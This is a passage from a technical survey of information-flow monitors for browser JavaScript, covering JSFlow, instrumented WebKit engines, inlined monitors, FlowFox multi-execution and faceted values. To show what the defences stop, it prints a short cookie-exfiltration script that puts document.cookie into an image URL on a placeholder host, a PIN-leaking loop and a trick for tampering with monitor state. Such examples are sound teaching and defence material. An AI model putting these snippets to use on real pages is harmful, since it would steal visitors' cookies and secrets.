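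The proof relies on a supporting theorem, *confinement*, which states that code running under a high pc changes nothing low. When two runs reach an `if` with a low condition, the condition has the same value in both, so they take the same branch. If the condition is high, they may take different branches, but neither branch can change anything low. In both cases the runs still agree on everything low afterwards.

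JSFlow's *transparency* theorem guarantees that if a program finishes under the monitor, its result, with the labels removed, is the same as it would be without the monitor. The theorem doesn't rule out false stops, in which the monitor halts a harmless script.

The core language includes objects with prototypes, functions as values, exceptions, `eval`, `with` and the upgrade annotations. Hedin and Sabelfeld used Coq, a program that verifies mathematical proofs, to check the hardest parts of their 2012 proof, including the cases for writing to properties and catching exceptions. The 2016 paper revised the rules for writing and deleting properties and gave a new written proof.

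The theorems don't cover several features of JSFlow. In the core language, each function has exactly one return statement, at the end, so the proof needs no return label. The core also leaves out labeled jumps, automatic conversions and nearly all of the built-in library, and it has a single pc instead of the stack. The proof uses only two labels, although Hedin and colleagues consider the extension to sets of origins mostly mechanical.

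The evidence for the full interpreter comes from testing. JSFlow passes all the standard-compliant tests for non-strict code in the test suite for SpiderMonkey, Firefox's engine. This is good evidence that it computes the right results, but conformance tests don't show that every result has the right label. In October 2014, @steike reported in *Breaking JSFlow with a magic trick* that JSFlow left some built-in state unlabeled. A later version of the online demo corrected part of this.

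Hedin and colleagues suggest narrowing the gap between the proof and the program with a specialised type checker for JSFlow's own code. Every flow in a script is also a flow in the interpreter, so the checker could confirm that JSFlow handles the label wherever it uses a labeled value. They had not built such a checker.

In *Precise Information Flow Control for JavaScript*, Quinaz proposes to avoid hand-written rules for JavaScript altogether. The language standard has grown to about 1,000 pages, and even a simple assignment can trigger hidden steps. Quinaz argues that earlier monitors offer no guarantee of catching every implicit flow in the language. This is true of JSFlow's full interpreter but not of its proven core. Quinaz's system translates each script into a much simpler language called ECMA-SL, using an implementation that follows the standard line by line. The hidden steps, such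 as the choice between `valueOf` and `toString`, become ordinary ECMA-SL code, so the monitor needs rules only for that language's few constructs.

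## Placing the monitor in the browser engine or in rewritten scripts

JSFlow runs a page's scripts in its own interpreter, so they lose the speed of the browser's optimized engine. Developers can keep that engine by adding labels to it, or by leaving it unchanged and rewriting each script to carry its own labels.

### One bit per domain

Bichhawat, Rajani and colleagues modified the WebKit engine in *Information Flow Control in WebKit's JavaScript Bytecode* (2014). WebKit compiles a script into *bytecode*, a list of simple instructions such as "add these two values" or "jump to instruction 12", which an interpreter carries out. The researchers added about 4,500 lines of code, nearly all of it in the interpreter, and barely changed the compiler.

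Each label is a 64-bit number in which every bit stands for one web domain. If the lender's domain has the label 0001 and the analytics company's has 0010, a value computed from both domains' data gets 0011. The monitor combines the labels with a bitwise or, a very fast processor operation that sets every bit that is set in either input.

Kerschbaumer, Hennigan and colleagues describe a similar system for WebKit in *Towards Precise and Efficient Information Flow Control in Web Browsers*. It reserves one bit as a flag. Once a page exceeds 63 domains, the system sets the flag and uses the other 63 bits to point into a table of longer labels, which is slower. The 500 popular pages they visited used 12 domains on average.

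Scripts can't tamper with labels inside the engine because JavaScript has no way to access them. The monitor also checks the compiler's output rather than the source code, so it would catch a leak that a compiler error introduced into a harmless script.

### Where a branch ends

When a script branches on a secret, the monitor raises the pc. It must then lower the pc at the right moment, or it would treat everything afterwards as secret. For a simple `if`, an interpreter that works on source code can do this at the closing brace. Bytecode has no braces and uses jumps for all control flow except function calls.

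Source code can also jump out of a block, as in this loop:

```
l = 1;
while (1) {
  ...
  if (h) { break; }
  l = 0;
  break;
}
```

Afterwards l is 1 if h is true and 0 if h is false, although no write to l is inside a block that depends on h. In simplified bytecode, the program looks like this:

```
1  l = 1
2  ...
3  if h is false, jump to 5
4  jump to 7
5  l = 0
6  jump to 7
7  (code after the loop)
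```

For each branch, the monitor computes the *immediate post-dominator*, the first instruction that runs whichever way the branch goes. For the branch at line 3, this is line 7, because one path goes through line 4 and the other through lines 5 and 6 before they meet there. When the script reaches line 3, the monitor puts a high pc label on a stack, together with the position of line 7. It removes the label when the script reaches line 7.

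If h is true, the script jumps from line 4 to line 7, and l is still 1 and low. If h is false, the script reaches line 5 while the pc is high, and the no-sensitive-upgrade rule blocks the write. (The paper gives the blocked write as `l = 1`, but that one happens before the loop.)

JSFlow also prevents this leak, but it needs an annotation before a script may break out of a loop when the break depends on a secret. The WebKit monitor doesn't need the annotation, and it can also treat the code on line 2 as public because that code runs before the script tests h.

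When WebKit compiles a function, the monitor builds a graph once of all the possible jumps in it and uses the graph to find the post-dominators. Just, Cleary and colleagues (2011), in *Information Flow Analysis for JavaScript*, had already combined runtime tracking with this kind of analysis in a production engine, but they ignored leaks through exceptions. Bichhawat (2015), in *Post-Dominator Analysis for Precisely Handling Implicit Flows*, reports a proof that no other way of setting the pc is more precise.

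### Exceptions that cross functions

An exception can carry control out of one function and into another:

```
function outer() {
  l = 0;
  try { inner(); } catch (err) { l = 1; }
  return l;
}
function inner() {
  if (h) { throw "stop"; }
}
```

The two paths from `if (h)` meet outside `inner`, at `return l`, because one returns to `outer` normally and the other jumps to the `catch` block. But `inner` may have many callers, and the meeting point depends on which one called it. Building a new graph for every call would take a lot of computation.

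Bichhawat and colleagues solve this with a *synthetic exit node*, an artificial last instruction in every function that may throw an exception without catching it. Normal returns and uncaught exceptions both lead to this node. From there, control passes to the caller or to the nearest exception handler among the functions still running. No jump in a function's graph leaves that function, so the monitor has to build each graph only once.

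In the example, this works as follows:

1. The function `outer` sets l to 0 and calls `inner`. The call might throw an exception, so the monitor treats it as a branch. It puts a low pc label on the stack, to be removed at `return l`.
2. In `inner`, the script tests h. Both paths lead to the exit node of `inner`, so the monitor adds no new entry to the stack. Instead it raises the existing entry to high.
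3. If h is false, `inner` returns normally through its exit node. The pc stays high until the script reaches `return l`, where the monitor removes the entry. The function `outer` returns a low 0.
4. If h is true, the `throw` leads to the exit node and from there to the `catch` block. The pc is still high, so the monitor blocks `l = 1`.

JSFlow would stop the same script earlier, at the `throw`, unless an annotation had raised the exception label. The WebKit monitor allows the exception and intervenes only when the handler writes to something public, so a handler that changes only secret data can run without annotations.

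Many bytecode instructions can throw exceptions, so the pc could stay high for long stretches. To avoid this, the monitor leaves out the exit nodes when no running function has a handler. An uncaught exception then ends the script. The guarantee excludes what an attacker learns from the script ending, but it requires the error message to stay hidden. The researchers returned to the subject in *Permissive runtime information flow control in the presence of exceptions* (2021).

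### Writes that nothing reads

These traces use the plain no-sensitive-upgrade rule. In WebKit, this rule would stop many harmless scripts because the compiler often generates *dead assignments* inside branches. A dead assignment stores a value in a register, one of the interpreter's slots for local variables, but no later instruction reads that value. A web developer can't remove such an assignment because it doesn't appear in the source code.

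Bichhawat and colleagues therefore use a *deferred no-sensitive-upgrade check*. When a script writes to a low register under a high pc, the monitor allows the write but marks the value as partially leaked. If the script later overwrites the register with a public value outside any secret branch, the mark disappears. The monitor stops the script only if the script uses the marked value in a way others could observe, such as branching on it or storing it in an object. In the loop example, if l is in a register, the script can run past `l = 0` and stops only when it uses l in such a way.

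The idea of marking values comes from Austin and Flanagan, but they allow a script to store a marked value in an object. The WebKit monitor doesn't, because of programs like this:

```
l = 0;
if (h) { l = 1; }
obj.a = l;
```

If h is 0, the last line stores an ordinary public 0. Nothing in that run shows that the value would have been marked if h had been 1, so the monitor can't hide the 0 from anyone outside the script who can read the object. Instead, it has to stop the script at the last line when h is 1. Registers can hold marked values safely because other scripts can't access them directly.

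The researchers modeled WebKit's bytecode from about 20,000 lines of interpreter code and proved noninterference for terminating runs of the model. The model includes 69 of the 147 instructions, and the rest are mostly faster versions of those. It also covers early returns and jumps out of loops, which the core language in JSFlow's proof does not.

The theorem applies to a single run of the interpreter, but a real page starts the interpreter again for every click or key press. The 2014 monitor also didn't follow data through built-in functions or the DOM. *Information Flow Control for Event Handling and the DOM in Web Browsers* (Rajani, Bichhawat and colleagues, 2015) extended the monitor to the DOM and to events.

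### Labels in compiled machine code

The bytecode monitor works only with the JIT compiler switched off. In *Information Flow Tracking meets Just-In-Time Compilation*, Kerschbaumer, Hennigan and colleagues modified one of WebKit's JIT compilers so that the machine code it produces also computes labels.

Their earlier system expanded every value from 64 to 128 bits to make room for a label. The new one fits a 16-bit label into the original 64 bits. WebKit left those 16 bits unused in whole numbers, and the researchers freed them in references to objects by limiting the memory for objects to 4 GB, which shortens their addresses.

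Sixteen bits are enough for 16 domains, and none of the 100 pages tested used more than 13 domains. But numbers with a fractional part need all 64 bits, so the system treats them as if all the domains had influenced them. On the loan calculator, a monthly instalment of 512.37 would get the highest label even if no secret data was used to calculate it.

To add two whole numbers a and b, the machine code does roughly this:

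```
label  = a | b           // combine the labels (and, as a side effect, the values)
label  = label | pc      // add the label of the pc
label  = label & mask    // keep only the 16 label bits
result = a + b           // add the values
result = result | label  // attach the label
```

For control flow, the compiler inserts instructions that raise the pc after a condition and lower it when the branch ends. A `break` needs special treatment, as in this function, which counts up to a secret PIN:

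```
function stealpin(secret) {
  for (var i = 0; i < 10000; i++) {
    if (i == secret) { break; }
  }
  return i;
}
```

When i reaches the PIN, the system raises the pc for the rest of the function, so the returned number carries the PIN's label. This is less precise than using post-dominators, which would let the system lower the pc after the loop.

The system doesn't catch information that a script reveals by not taking a branch, so the three-line leak from the introduction would succeed. The no-sensitive-upgrade rule would stop the leak, but Kerschbaumer and colleagues rejected it because halting scripts would annoy users, and concentrated on speed instead. Their system follows more flows than taint tracking, but it can't guarantee noninterference against a script written to exploit this gap.

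It's also unclear how much of the language the compiler covers. The researchers describe tests of `if` statements, several kinds of loop and `eval`, but they also write that they instrumented no control structure beyond the basic `for` loop, and that their handling of exceptions and property lookups is incomplete. On their 100 test pages, the JIT version found 1,173 suspicious flows, and an interpreter version had found 1,155 the day before. This suggests that the two versions track much the same flows, but both have the same gap in coverage.

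### The upkeep of a modified engine

Browser engines change quickly. In March 2012, WebKit replaced the interpreter that Kerschbaumer and colleagues had modified, and they had to run their measurements on the old one.

Chudnov and Naumann, in *Inlined Information Flow Monitoring for JavaScript* (2015), argue that a modified engine is useful only in its own browser and may be impossible to maintain without the vendor's help. They also consider it impractical to add labels to a modern JIT compiler, because an engine often has several complicated compilers for different kinds of code. They prefer to *inline* the monitor by rewriting each script to do the tracking itself. An inlined monitor can run in any browser, and its developers have to keep up with changes to JavaScript but not to each engine.

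### Shadow variables

Magazinius, Russo and Sabelfeld, in *On-the-fly Inlining of Dynamic Security Monitors* (2010), give every variable a *shadow variable* that holds its label. One more shadow variable holds the pc. Here true stands for high and false for low. Adapted slightly to ordinary JavaScript, their version of `if (h) { l = true; }` is:

```
saved = pc;
pc = pc || shadow.h;
if (h) {
  if (!pc || shadow.l) {
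    shadow.l = pc;
    l = true;
  } else {
    throw new Error();
  }
}
pc = saved;
```

The second line raises the pc if h is secret. The inner `if` applies the no-sensitive-upgrade rule by allowing the write only if the pc is low or l is already high. The last line restores the old pc. The rewriting also applies to any text the script passes to `eval`.

*On-The-Fly Inlining Of Dynamic Security Monitors* proves noninterference for a small language with `eval` but without objects or exceptions. In that language, a blocked program loops forever. The JavaScript version throws an error instead. A script could catch that error and keep running, and the proof doesn't cover this case. The researchers rewrote their first test programs by hand, and the 2012 journal version adds results from automatic rewriting.

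A rewritten script runs side by side with its own monitor, so a hostile script may try to change the labels. It isn't enough to ban the name `pc` from scripts, because a script can build the name as text and look it up:

```
x = 'pc'; this[x]
```

A script could also replace the function that rewrites code with one that returns its input unchanged. Magazinius and colleagues suggest hiding the shadow variables in an object with a unique name and restricting which language features scripts may use.

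### Boxed values

Chudnov and Naumann built JEST, an inlined monitor that supports almost all of non-strict ECMAScript 5, with the `with` statement as the main omission. JEST stores every value in a *box*, an object that holds the value, its label and some type information. The label therefore stays with the value in both variables and properties, whereas shadow variables need separate bookkeeping for each.

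JEST replaces most operations with calls to the monitor's functions. With shorter names than the real ones, `while (a > 10) { a = a - 1; }` becomes:

```
enter(1);
while (toBoolean(update(1, greater(a, low(10)))).v) {
  assign(a, subtract(a, low(1)));
}
exit();
```

Here `low(10)` puts the constant 10 in a box with a public label. `greater` compares two boxed values and combines their labels, and `update` raises the pc to the label of the result. `.v` extracts the plain boolean from its box so that the browser's own `while` can test it. `assign` checks the no-sensitive-upgrade rule before changing `a`. `enter` and `exit` mark the code that depends on the condition.

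The function calls also preserve the script's behaviour by evaluating each operand only once. If an addition such as `y++ + x` were written out inline, `y++` would appear twice, once for its value and once for its label, and y would be incremented twice.

Like the WebKit monitor, JEST analyses the possible jumps within each function to decide when to lower the pc label. Its handling of exceptions that cross functions is simpler. It saves the stack of pc labels at the start of a `try` block and restores it in the `finally` part.

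To protect the monitor, JEST adds a random prefix to the names of all its variables and keeps them inside a function, where scripts can't list them. A script could guess a name only by using `eval`, and JEST rejects any evaluated code that refers to a monitor variable. JEST also replaces the browser's built-in objects with its own versions, which unbox values before calling the real functions and then box the results. If a script gets hold of an original function, the call fails because the function isn't boxed, which may break the page but doesn't leak anything.

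Chudnov and Naumann tested JEST on web applications they wrote themselves, each in honest and malicious versions. In one, a shop includes a form from a payment company. The shop must not see the card number, and the payment company must not see what the customer ordered. JEST stopped all the malicious versions. The honest ones worked after the researchers added a declassification annotation to the payment example and an upgrade annotation to one with advertisements. The results are encouraging, but the applications were small and their developers knew how the monitor worked. There is no proof for JEST itself. The JIT compiler sped up the monitor's own functions but not the rewritten scripts.

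### Extension, proxy or website

A modified engine can monitor every script because it runs them all, but a monitor written in JavaScript first has to get into the page and take control of the scripts there. *Architectures for Inlining Security Monitors in Web Applications* (Magazinius, Hedin and Sabelfeld, 2014) compares four ways of doing this, using JSFlow as the monitor. JSFlow interprets scripts instead of rewriting their individual operations, but an inlined monitor such as JEST raises many of the same questions about delivery.

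| Delivery | What happens to a script it misses | Best suited to |
|---|---|---|
| Browser extension | The script doesn't run | Private users |
| Web proxy | The script runs outside the monitor | Companies |
| Suffix proxy | The script runs outside the monitor | Private users who want to protect particular sites |
| The website itself | The script runs outside the monitor | Site developers |

The extension turns off JavaScript in the browser and passes the text of each script to the monitor. This makes the monitor hard to bypass but also gives it the same privileges as the browser, so a bug in the monitor could endanger the whole browser. An extension works only in the browser it was written for. Some pages also break because browsers don't let extensions call `document.write`, a function that scripts use to insert text into a page while it loads.

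A *web proxy* is a server that fetches pages on the browser's behalf. It can add the monitor to each page and wrap every script in a call to the monitor. The proxy must find all the scripts, which is difficult because browsers accept malformed HTML. If the proxy and the browser interpret a page differently, an attacker can hide a script from the proxy. The script then runs unmonitored in the same page as the monitor and may disable it. Magazinius and colleagues reduce this risk with a parser that follows the HTML5 standard.

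The proxy also has to decrypt secure connections in order to change the pages, so its operator can read everything sent over them, including passwords. Companies often run a trusted proxy already, but a private user may have good reason to trust a bank more than the proxy.

With a *suffix proxy*, the user chooses which pages to protect by adding the proxy's name to the address, as in `google.com.proxy.domain`. The browser treats this as a different origin from `google.com`, so the protected page can't use the cookies from ordinary visits. But all protected sites share the parent domain `proxy.domain`. Browsers allowed pages with a common parent domain to opt out of the same-origin policy between them, so two unrelated sites could access each other's data unless the monitor prevented it.

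Magazinius and colleagues also tried JSFlow on websites that rate password strength. As with the loan calculators, one of these sites could keep using Google Analytics without revealing what the visitor typed.

A website can also include the monitor itself and use it only for third-party scripts, while its own code runs at full speed. The loan calculator's owner could confine the analytics script without asking visitors to install anything. But the owner's code can change the monitor's state, so a mistake there may let the analytics script escape. Automatically sharing variables between the trusted code and the analytics script is also dangerous, because the script could change a value that the trusted code relies on. Magazinius and colleagues therefore recommend that developers pass each piece of data across manually, which requires some understanding of how the monitor works.

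## Running each script once per security level

Secure multi-execution runs a script once per security level, so it doesn't need to label the script's values or keep a pc label. It is also designed to avoid stopping secure scripts, which a monitor can do by mistake.

Devriese and Piessens proposed the technique in *Noninterference Through Secure Multi-Execution* (2010), and other researchers had also developed it independently. In *FlowFox* (2012), De Groef, Devriese and colleagues built it into Firefox 8 with about 1,400 new lines of code, less than a third of what the WebKit monitor needed.

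### Four rules for input and output

With two levels, FlowFox runs each script twice, as a low run and a high run. The policy gives every call to a browser function a level. FlowFox treats such a call as an output (the request to the browser) followed by an input (the value that comes back). It then applies four rules:

1. Each run performs only the calls at its own level.
2. It skips outputs at any other level.
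3. If the low run asks for a high input, it gets a default value instead.
4. If the high run asks for a low input, it gets the value that the low run has already read.

De Groef and colleagues illustrate the rules with a script that tries to steal a cookie. Slightly shortened, it reads:

```
var url = "//host/image.jpg?" + document.cookie;
var i = new Image(); i.src = url;
if (i.width > 50) { /* change the layout */ }
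```

The policy labels reading the cookie as high, with an empty string as the default value. It labels reading the image's width as low, as well as setting the image's address, which sends a request to a server. FlowFox completes the low run before it starts the high run.

| Step | Low run | High run |
|---|---|---|
| Read the cookie | Gets an empty string | Gets the real cookie |
| Set the image's address | Fetches the image, with no cookie in the address | Skips the request |
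| Read the width | Gets the real width, say 100 | Reuses the 100 |

The script runs twice, but the browser performs each of the three calls only once. The server receives a single request, which can't contain the cookie because the run that sent it never had the cookie.

### Copying the scripts but not the browser

Two earlier projects took the simpler approach of running two complete copies of the browser as separate processes. The policy then has to label what is visible to the operating system, such as files, network connections and mouse events. At that level, there is no way to determine which tab or page element a key press is meant for. De Groef and colleagues give the example of an email that the user types into a webmail page. A system that copies the whole browser couldn't stop a script from leaking the text to another company whose site is open in a second tab, because it can't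 determine which site the text was meant for.

FlowFox therefore copies only the scripts, and both runs share one browser and one DOM. A policy can then refer to a particular page element or web address. But a browser offers scripts far more functions than an operating system offers programs, so there is more to label.

Inside the JavaScript engine, every property of an object has a security level. An object can have two properties called `x`, a low one with the value 0 and a high one with the value 5, and each run can access only the one at its own level. FlowFox runs the code that compiles and executes scripts in a loop over the levels, from lowest to highest. Code passed to `eval` needs no special treatment, because each run evaluates the text it has built.

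Firefox already had a layer that converted values whenever a script called a DOM function, so FlowFox can apply the four rules in that one place. In simplified form:

```
function process(call, args, level) {
  var rule = policy(call, args);
  if (level == rule.level) {
    var result = perform(call, args);
    cache.store(result, call, args);
    return result;
  }
  if (level > rule.level) { return cache.retrieve(call, args); }
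  return rule.defaultValue;
}
```

In the cookie example, the low run stores the width in the cache, and the high run retrieves it from there.

Events are inputs too. Both runs handle a low event, such as the page finishing loading, and the low run goes first. Only the high run handles a high event. Suppose the policy makes key presses high and a script responds to each one by loading an image whose address contains the key. The high run receives the key press but skips the image request, so the server receives no sign that the visitor pressed a key. The policy sets an event's level by labeling the calls that register handlers for it, and FlowFox stores each handler with the level of the run that registered it.

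### Rules for cookies and selected text

A FlowFox rule has the form

R[D] : C₁ → l₁, …, Cₙ → lₙ ↪ dv

R is the rule's name and D is the browser function it covers. FlowFox tests the conditions C₁ to Cₙ in order, and the first one that holds determines the level of the call. If none holds, the call is low. The last part, dv, is the default value for a run that may not see the real one. The rules for cookies and selected text need no real condition:

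```
R1[document.cookie]     : true → H ↪ ""
R6[window.getSelection] : true → H ↪ ""
```

R1 labels both reading and writing the cookie as high. R6 is meant for scripts like Tynt's, which send copied text to the company that made them. Under R6, Tynt's server gets an empty string each time a reader copies a passage.

Any function without a rule is low, so a browser with an empty policy behaves like an ordinary one. This keeps policies short, but a rule for the source alone is often not enough. In the loan calculator, if the income is high and writing to the page is low, the low run writes the result, and the page shows an instalment computed from the default income. The policy must also label writes to the instalment element high. De Groef and colleagues likewise label both the cookie and the background colour high for a script that sets the page's background colour from a cookie.

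Conditions can depend on where a request goes. One published rule makes a request high if it goes to the page's own origin. The high run then sends that request with the real data, while the low run sends requests to all other servers.

Such conditions are easy to get wrong. In De Groef (2016), in *Client- and Server-Side Security Technologies for JavaScript Web Applications*, the code for this rule contains the following test:

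```
var isSameOrigin = function ([url]) {
  return (url.indexOf("same-origin") == -1);
};
```

Here "same-origin" stands for the site's own host name. `indexOf` returns -1 if the text does not occur in the address, so the test is reversed. With this policy, the high run would send real data to every server except the site's own.

### Why compliant scripts behave as before

Algehed and Flanagan (2020), in *Transparent IFC Enforcement*, write multi-execution as a formula. Let p be a program and x its labeled inputs. Let x↓ℓ be the inputs that level ℓ may see, and let @ℓ select the outputs with exactly the label ℓ. Multi-execution then produces

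ME\[p\](x) = ⋃ { p(x↓ℓ)@ℓ : ℓ is a level }

Each level's outputs come from a run that receives only the inputs visible at that level, which guarantees noninterference for any program. If p already satisfies noninterference, the hidden inputs don't affect its outputs at level ℓ, so p(x↓ℓ)@ℓ equals p(x)@ℓ. Together, the runs produce exactly the outputs p would have produced by itself. Researchers call this property *precision* or *transparency*. The same reasoning applies to FlowFox, which replaces hidden inputs with default values instead of leaving them out.

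Take the harmless program that JSFlow can run only with an upgrade annotation:

```
l = false;
if (h) { l = true; }
```

The low run uses false as the default for h and ends with l false. If h is actually true, the high run ends with l true. Neither run has to be stopped, so the script needs no annotation. JSFlow guarantees an unchanged result only for scripts it allows to finish.

The formula assumes that every run finishes. A program that loops forever unless it receives a secret never finishes its low run, even if it leaks nothing else. Precision therefore holds only for programs that still finish when their secret inputs are missing.

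If a script does leak, FlowFox replaces the secret with the default value and lets the script continue. For example, De Groef and colleagues give rules that report every mouse position as 0 to outside parties. A company that records clicks to see which parts of a page attract attention would see every click in the top left corner, and the visitor would notice nothing. In the test on 500 popular sites, one site violated the cookie policy, and FlowFox could still display it correctly with a suitable default.

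De Groef considers silent repair a good choice for a browser because users tend to ignore security warnings, but it also means nobody learns about the leak. De Groef points to a proposal by Rafnsson and Sabelfeld to compare the public operations of the two runs and report any difference as a possible attack. This comparison would require a JavaScript engine that can pause one run and switch to the other. De Groef also warns that a website can easily detect FlowFox, and could then slow itself down to make users switch back to an ordinary browser.

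### When the two runs disagree

The high run can reuse the low run's inputs only if both runs make the same calls. This requires scripts to be deterministic, meaning that the same inputs always lead to the same behaviour. De Groef and colleagues treat JavaScript's sources of randomness as technical details that don't matter in practice, except for timers, which they handle as events. This seems optimistic, because a script that puts a random number into an image's address may draw a different number in each run, and the high run would then need the result for an image that the low run never loaded.

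The runs can also differ because of the secret. Suppose a script reads the page's title only if a cookie exists. The low run has an empty cookie and skips the call, so when the high run makes the call, it finds no stored title. The 2012 paper describes the stored result as guaranteed to exist, but that is true only if the low run made the same call. In De Groef's formal model, the high run then gets stuck, although De Groef notes that a more lenient rule would be equally secure. Strictly, such a script breaks the policy, because the request for the title counts as a low output that depends on a secret. But no outside server would see the request, so FlowFox can disrupt a script that most people would call harmless.

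A poorly chosen default value can crash the low run. For example, a script that processes a user name from the cookie may throw an exception if it gets an empty string instead. The low run sends all the low requests, so none would go out after the crash. De Groef encountered a few such crashes during testing and had to change the defaults.

### Labels that contradict each other

De Groef, Devriese and colleagues (2014) proved noninterference for a simplified model of FlowFox. In the model, a script can only call browser functions and register event handlers. The theorem concerns two visits to a page with the same script but possibly different secrets. If the script has received the same low inputs in both visits, its next low call must be the same.

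The proof covers leaks through scripts but not through the browser or anything outside it. Suppose a policy labels writing a cookie as high but reading one as low. The high run writes a secret into the cookie, and the low run, while handling a later event, reads it back as public data. The four rules allow both steps. The same kind of leak can happen outside the browser if a script sends high data to a server that returns it in a low message.

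A policy must therefore match how the browser's functions work together, which De Groef describes as difficult to check in general. Checking is easier for policies that only label certain reads as high, such as reading the selected text, because the script then has no high output through which to store a secret. But the loan calculator needs a high output to display the instalment. Its policy must therefore also label reads of that part of the page as high, or the analytics script could read the instalment there.

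### Outputs in a different order

FlowFox finishes the low run for an event before it starts the high run, so all the low calls happen before the high ones. De Groef gives the example of a script that shows the visitor how many bytes the page has sent and then sends a message. Reading the count is a high call, and sending is a low one. An ordinary browser reads the count first. In FlowFox, the low run sends the message before the high run reads the count, so the visitor sees a larger number even though the script leaks nothing.

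The formula treats the outputs as an unordered set, so it doesn't show this problem. The 2012 paper states that compliant scripts behave exactly as before. De Groef's thesis corrects this claim by saying that each level's outputs stay the same if nobody can compare the levels, but that FlowFox as a whole does not guarantee precision. Rafnsson and Sabelfeld proposed a way to preserve the order, but it needs more control over scheduling than FlowFox has.

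The schedule also affects what an attacker can learn from timing. *Secure Multi-Execution* (Devriese and Piessens, 2010) presents a theorem that covers timing as well as outputs, provided that the low run always goes first. FlowFox follows this order only within each event. If a visitor presses a key, the high run handles the key press, and the low run must wait to handle the next event. A hostile script could make the high run loop longer when the key is a 9 than when it is a 1, and then measure the delay with a timer in the low run.

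### The number of levels

De Groef and colleagues write that FlowFox can handle any number of levels, but with considerable overhead. According to De Groef's thesis, the prototype supports only two. With two levels, typical browsing tasks took around 20% longer.

If labels are sets of domains, the technique may need to run each script once for every possible set. Two domains have four sets (neither, either one alone, and both), and n domains have 2ⁿ. The popular pages that Kerschbaumer and colleagues visited used 12 domains on average, which could mean 4,096 runs of every script.

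### Faceted values

Most of these runs would repeat the same work, because most of a page's data doesn't depend on any secret. Austin and Flanagan, in *Multiple Facets for Dynamic Information Flow*, avoid much of the repetition by keeping several versions of individual values instead of running the whole script several times. They write a faceted value as

⟨k ? V_H : V_L⟩

Here k is a *principal*, a party with its own secrets, such as a web domain. Anyone allowed to read k's data sees the private facet V_H, and everyone else sees the public facet V_L. A value without facets looks the same to everyone.

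Operations on faceted values apply to each facet. If a script branches on a faceted value, the interpreter may have to run the code up to the end of the branch once for each facet. During each run, the pc records whose view the code is running for, and assignments change only that view.

Applied to the three-line leak from the introduction, this works as follows:

```
l = 1; t = 0;
if (h == 1) { t = 1; }
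if (t != 1) { l = 0; }
```

Suppose h is ⟨k ? 1 : undefined⟩, so the secret is 1 and the public sees no value.

1. The first line sets l to 1 and t to 0 for everyone.
2. The test `h == 1` is true for the private facet and false for the public one. The interpreter runs `t = 1` in the private view only, so t becomes ⟨k ? 1 : 0⟩.
3. The test `t != 1` is false in the private view and true in the public view. The interpreter runs `l = 0` in the public view only, so l becomes ⟨k ? 1 : 0⟩.

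If the secret is 0 instead, t stays 0 in both views, and l becomes 0 for everyone. The public sees l as 0 in either case and learns nothing about the secret. Someone who is allowed to read k's data sees the correct value, 1 or 0.

Austin and Flanagan show that the no-sensitive-upgrade rule halts a script exactly where their system would have to store a public facet containing a real value, as at `t = 1` here. They also prove that any script that finishes under the rule produces the same result with faceted values.

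With several principals, facets can contain other facets:

⟨k₁ ? 2 : 0⟩ + ⟨k₂ ? 1 : 0⟩ = ⟨k₁ ? ⟨k₂ ? 3 : 2⟩ : ⟨k₂ ? 1 : 0⟩⟩

A viewer who may read both principals' data sees 3, one who may read only k₁'s sees 2, one who may read only k₂'s sees 1, and the public sees 0. A single faceted run can therefore imitate 2ⁿ ordinary runs, but values that combine many principals' secrets can still grow very large.

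### Faceted values in Firefox

Austin and Flanagan built a prototype from Narcissus, a JavaScript interpreter, and Zaphod, a plugin that runs it inside Firefox. The `makePrivate` function turns a value into a faceted one whose public facet is undefined. JavaScript's `||` operator can then supply a default for the public facet, so `makePrivate(42) || 0` gives ⟨k ? 42 : 0⟩. The `getPublic` function extracts the public facet before data leaves the browser.

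In the paper's main example, an attacker has injected a script into a login page. The script intercepts the password on its way to a function that hashes, or scrambles, it. To remove any label from the password, the script writes it into an attribute of the page's title and reads it back by a different route. It then puts the result into the address of an image on the attacker's server. The attack fails because the prototype's version of the DOM stores both facets. The attacker's server receives only the public facet, while the site's own server still receives the real password.

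The prototype can still halt a harmless script, because it stops execution when an exception might leak a secret. *Multiple Facets for Dynamic Information Flow with Exceptions* (Austin, Schmitz and Flanagan, 2017) later extended the method to exceptions.

Deliberately releasing a secret is also easier with faceted values than with separate runs, because one value already holds both the private and public versions. Austin and Flanagan describe a declassification function that moves data from the private facet to the public one. It works only if untrusted data did not influence the decision to call it, so that an attacker can't trick the site's own code into releasing the password.

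To compare the methods, Austin and Flanagan built multi-execution into the same interpreter. They timed a program that performs eight hashing operations on a four-core computer. Each principal marked one of the inputs as private.

| Principals | Multi-execution, one run at a time | Multi-execution, parallel runs | Faceted values |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 274 s | 283 s | 311 s |
| 1 | 514 s | 284 s | 349 s |
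| 3 | 1,784 s | 598 s | 422 s |
| 5 | over an hour | 1,982 s | 503 s |
| 8 | over an hour | over an hour | 614 s |

With one or two principals, there were enough cores for all the runs, and parallel multi-execution was faster. With three or more, faceted values were faster, and each additional principal added only about 40 seconds. The test favours faceted values, though, because each principal's secret goes into a different hashing operation. If the program had combined the secrets, as in the addition above, the number of facets would have multiplied.

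### Limits on transparent enforcement

Algehed and Flanagan proved that any *black-box* method that is both secure and transparent (it leaves every secure program unchanged) needs time that grows exponentially with the number of principals. A black-box method can run a program on chosen inputs and observe the outputs but can't look inside it. Multi-execution in its basic form is such a method.

The proof uses the fact that a fast method can't try the inputs of every possible group of principals. Let S be a group whose inputs it never tries alone when everyone's inputs are present. Algehed and Flanagan construct three programs:

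- **empty** never outputs anything.
- **greater** sends S a message whenever all of S's inputs are present.
- **equal** sends S the message only if all of S's inputs are present and nobody else's are.

The programs `empty` and `greater` are secure, so the method must not change what they do. The program `equal` is insecure, because S can infer from a missing message that someone outside the group has supplied an input.

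When everyone's inputs are present, the method never tries the one case in which equal and empty differ, so it can't distinguish them and has to output nothing. When only S's inputs are present, it can't distinguish equal from greater, so it has to send the message. The leak therefore remains, which contradicts the assumption that the method is secure.

Faceted values aren't a black-box method, because the interpreter follows the program's individual operations. Algehed and Flanagan proved a weaker result for methods of this kind. If a fast transparent method existed, multi-execution could be made fast too, by using that method to find which levels appear in a program's output and then running the program only for those levels. They know of no way to make multi-execution fast for all programs, and they conjecture that none exists.

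Algehed and Flanagan's model covers programs that receive all their inputs at the start, whereas a web page keeps receiving new events. They expect events to make enforcement harder. Their results also concern guarantees for every possible program, so a method could still be fast on typical ones. In earlier work they describe, programmers specified by hand which levels a piece of code could affect, which reduced the overhead from exponential to polynomial. Someone had to analyse each program to do this, which isn't feasible for every script a browser loads. They still consider multi-execution usable where there are few levels, as in FlowFox.

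## Handling code that is created while the page runs

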